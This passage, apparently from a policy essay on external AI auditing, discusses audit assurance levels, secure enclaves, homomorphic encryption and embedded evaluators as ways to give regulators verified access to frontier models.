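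The paper defines four levels of assurance. The lowest matches the best current practice and relies heavily on information from the company. At the highest, auditors could rule out significant deception by the company, but the top two levels aren't feasible yet, according to the paper. Enclaves could help auditors reach them by showing that a result came from a particular model, though they couldn't show that the company had disclosed all its models.

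The EU's code of practice is closer to what an enclave can provide, because it directly addresses evaluators' access to models. But it doesn't specify how deep that access must be, as Charnock, Tlaie and colleagues (2026) note. An enclave that let an evaluator study a model's internals might well qualify, though an owner could argue that its ordinary API does too.

*Enabling External Scrutiny* argues that privacy technology has removed owners' best excuse for refusing access, and that legislators should require them to accept important research. The argument is strong for tests on the owner's premises but weaker when the weights have to be moved elsewhere, because TEE.fail has since given owners a good technical reason to refuse.

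### Using several methods together

An evaluator could combine homomorphic encryption, which hides the questions, with a proof that the owner ran the right model. This would leave very few parties to trust, but each method is too slow for a large model even on its own.

Combining embedded evaluators with enclaves would be more practical. In the Gemini trial, AVERI couldn't inspect all of Google's server software. Evaluators working inside a company could read that software, confirm that the hash of the weights matches the model in daily use, and check that nobody had altered the attestation service. A government could then send its secret questions to the enclave without showing them to the company or the embedded evaluators. Under Anthropic's current terms, METR might need special permission for this work, because code that runs a model reveals its architecture. Clubic reports that Anthropic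 generally tries to share such details when the stakes justify it, after an internal review.
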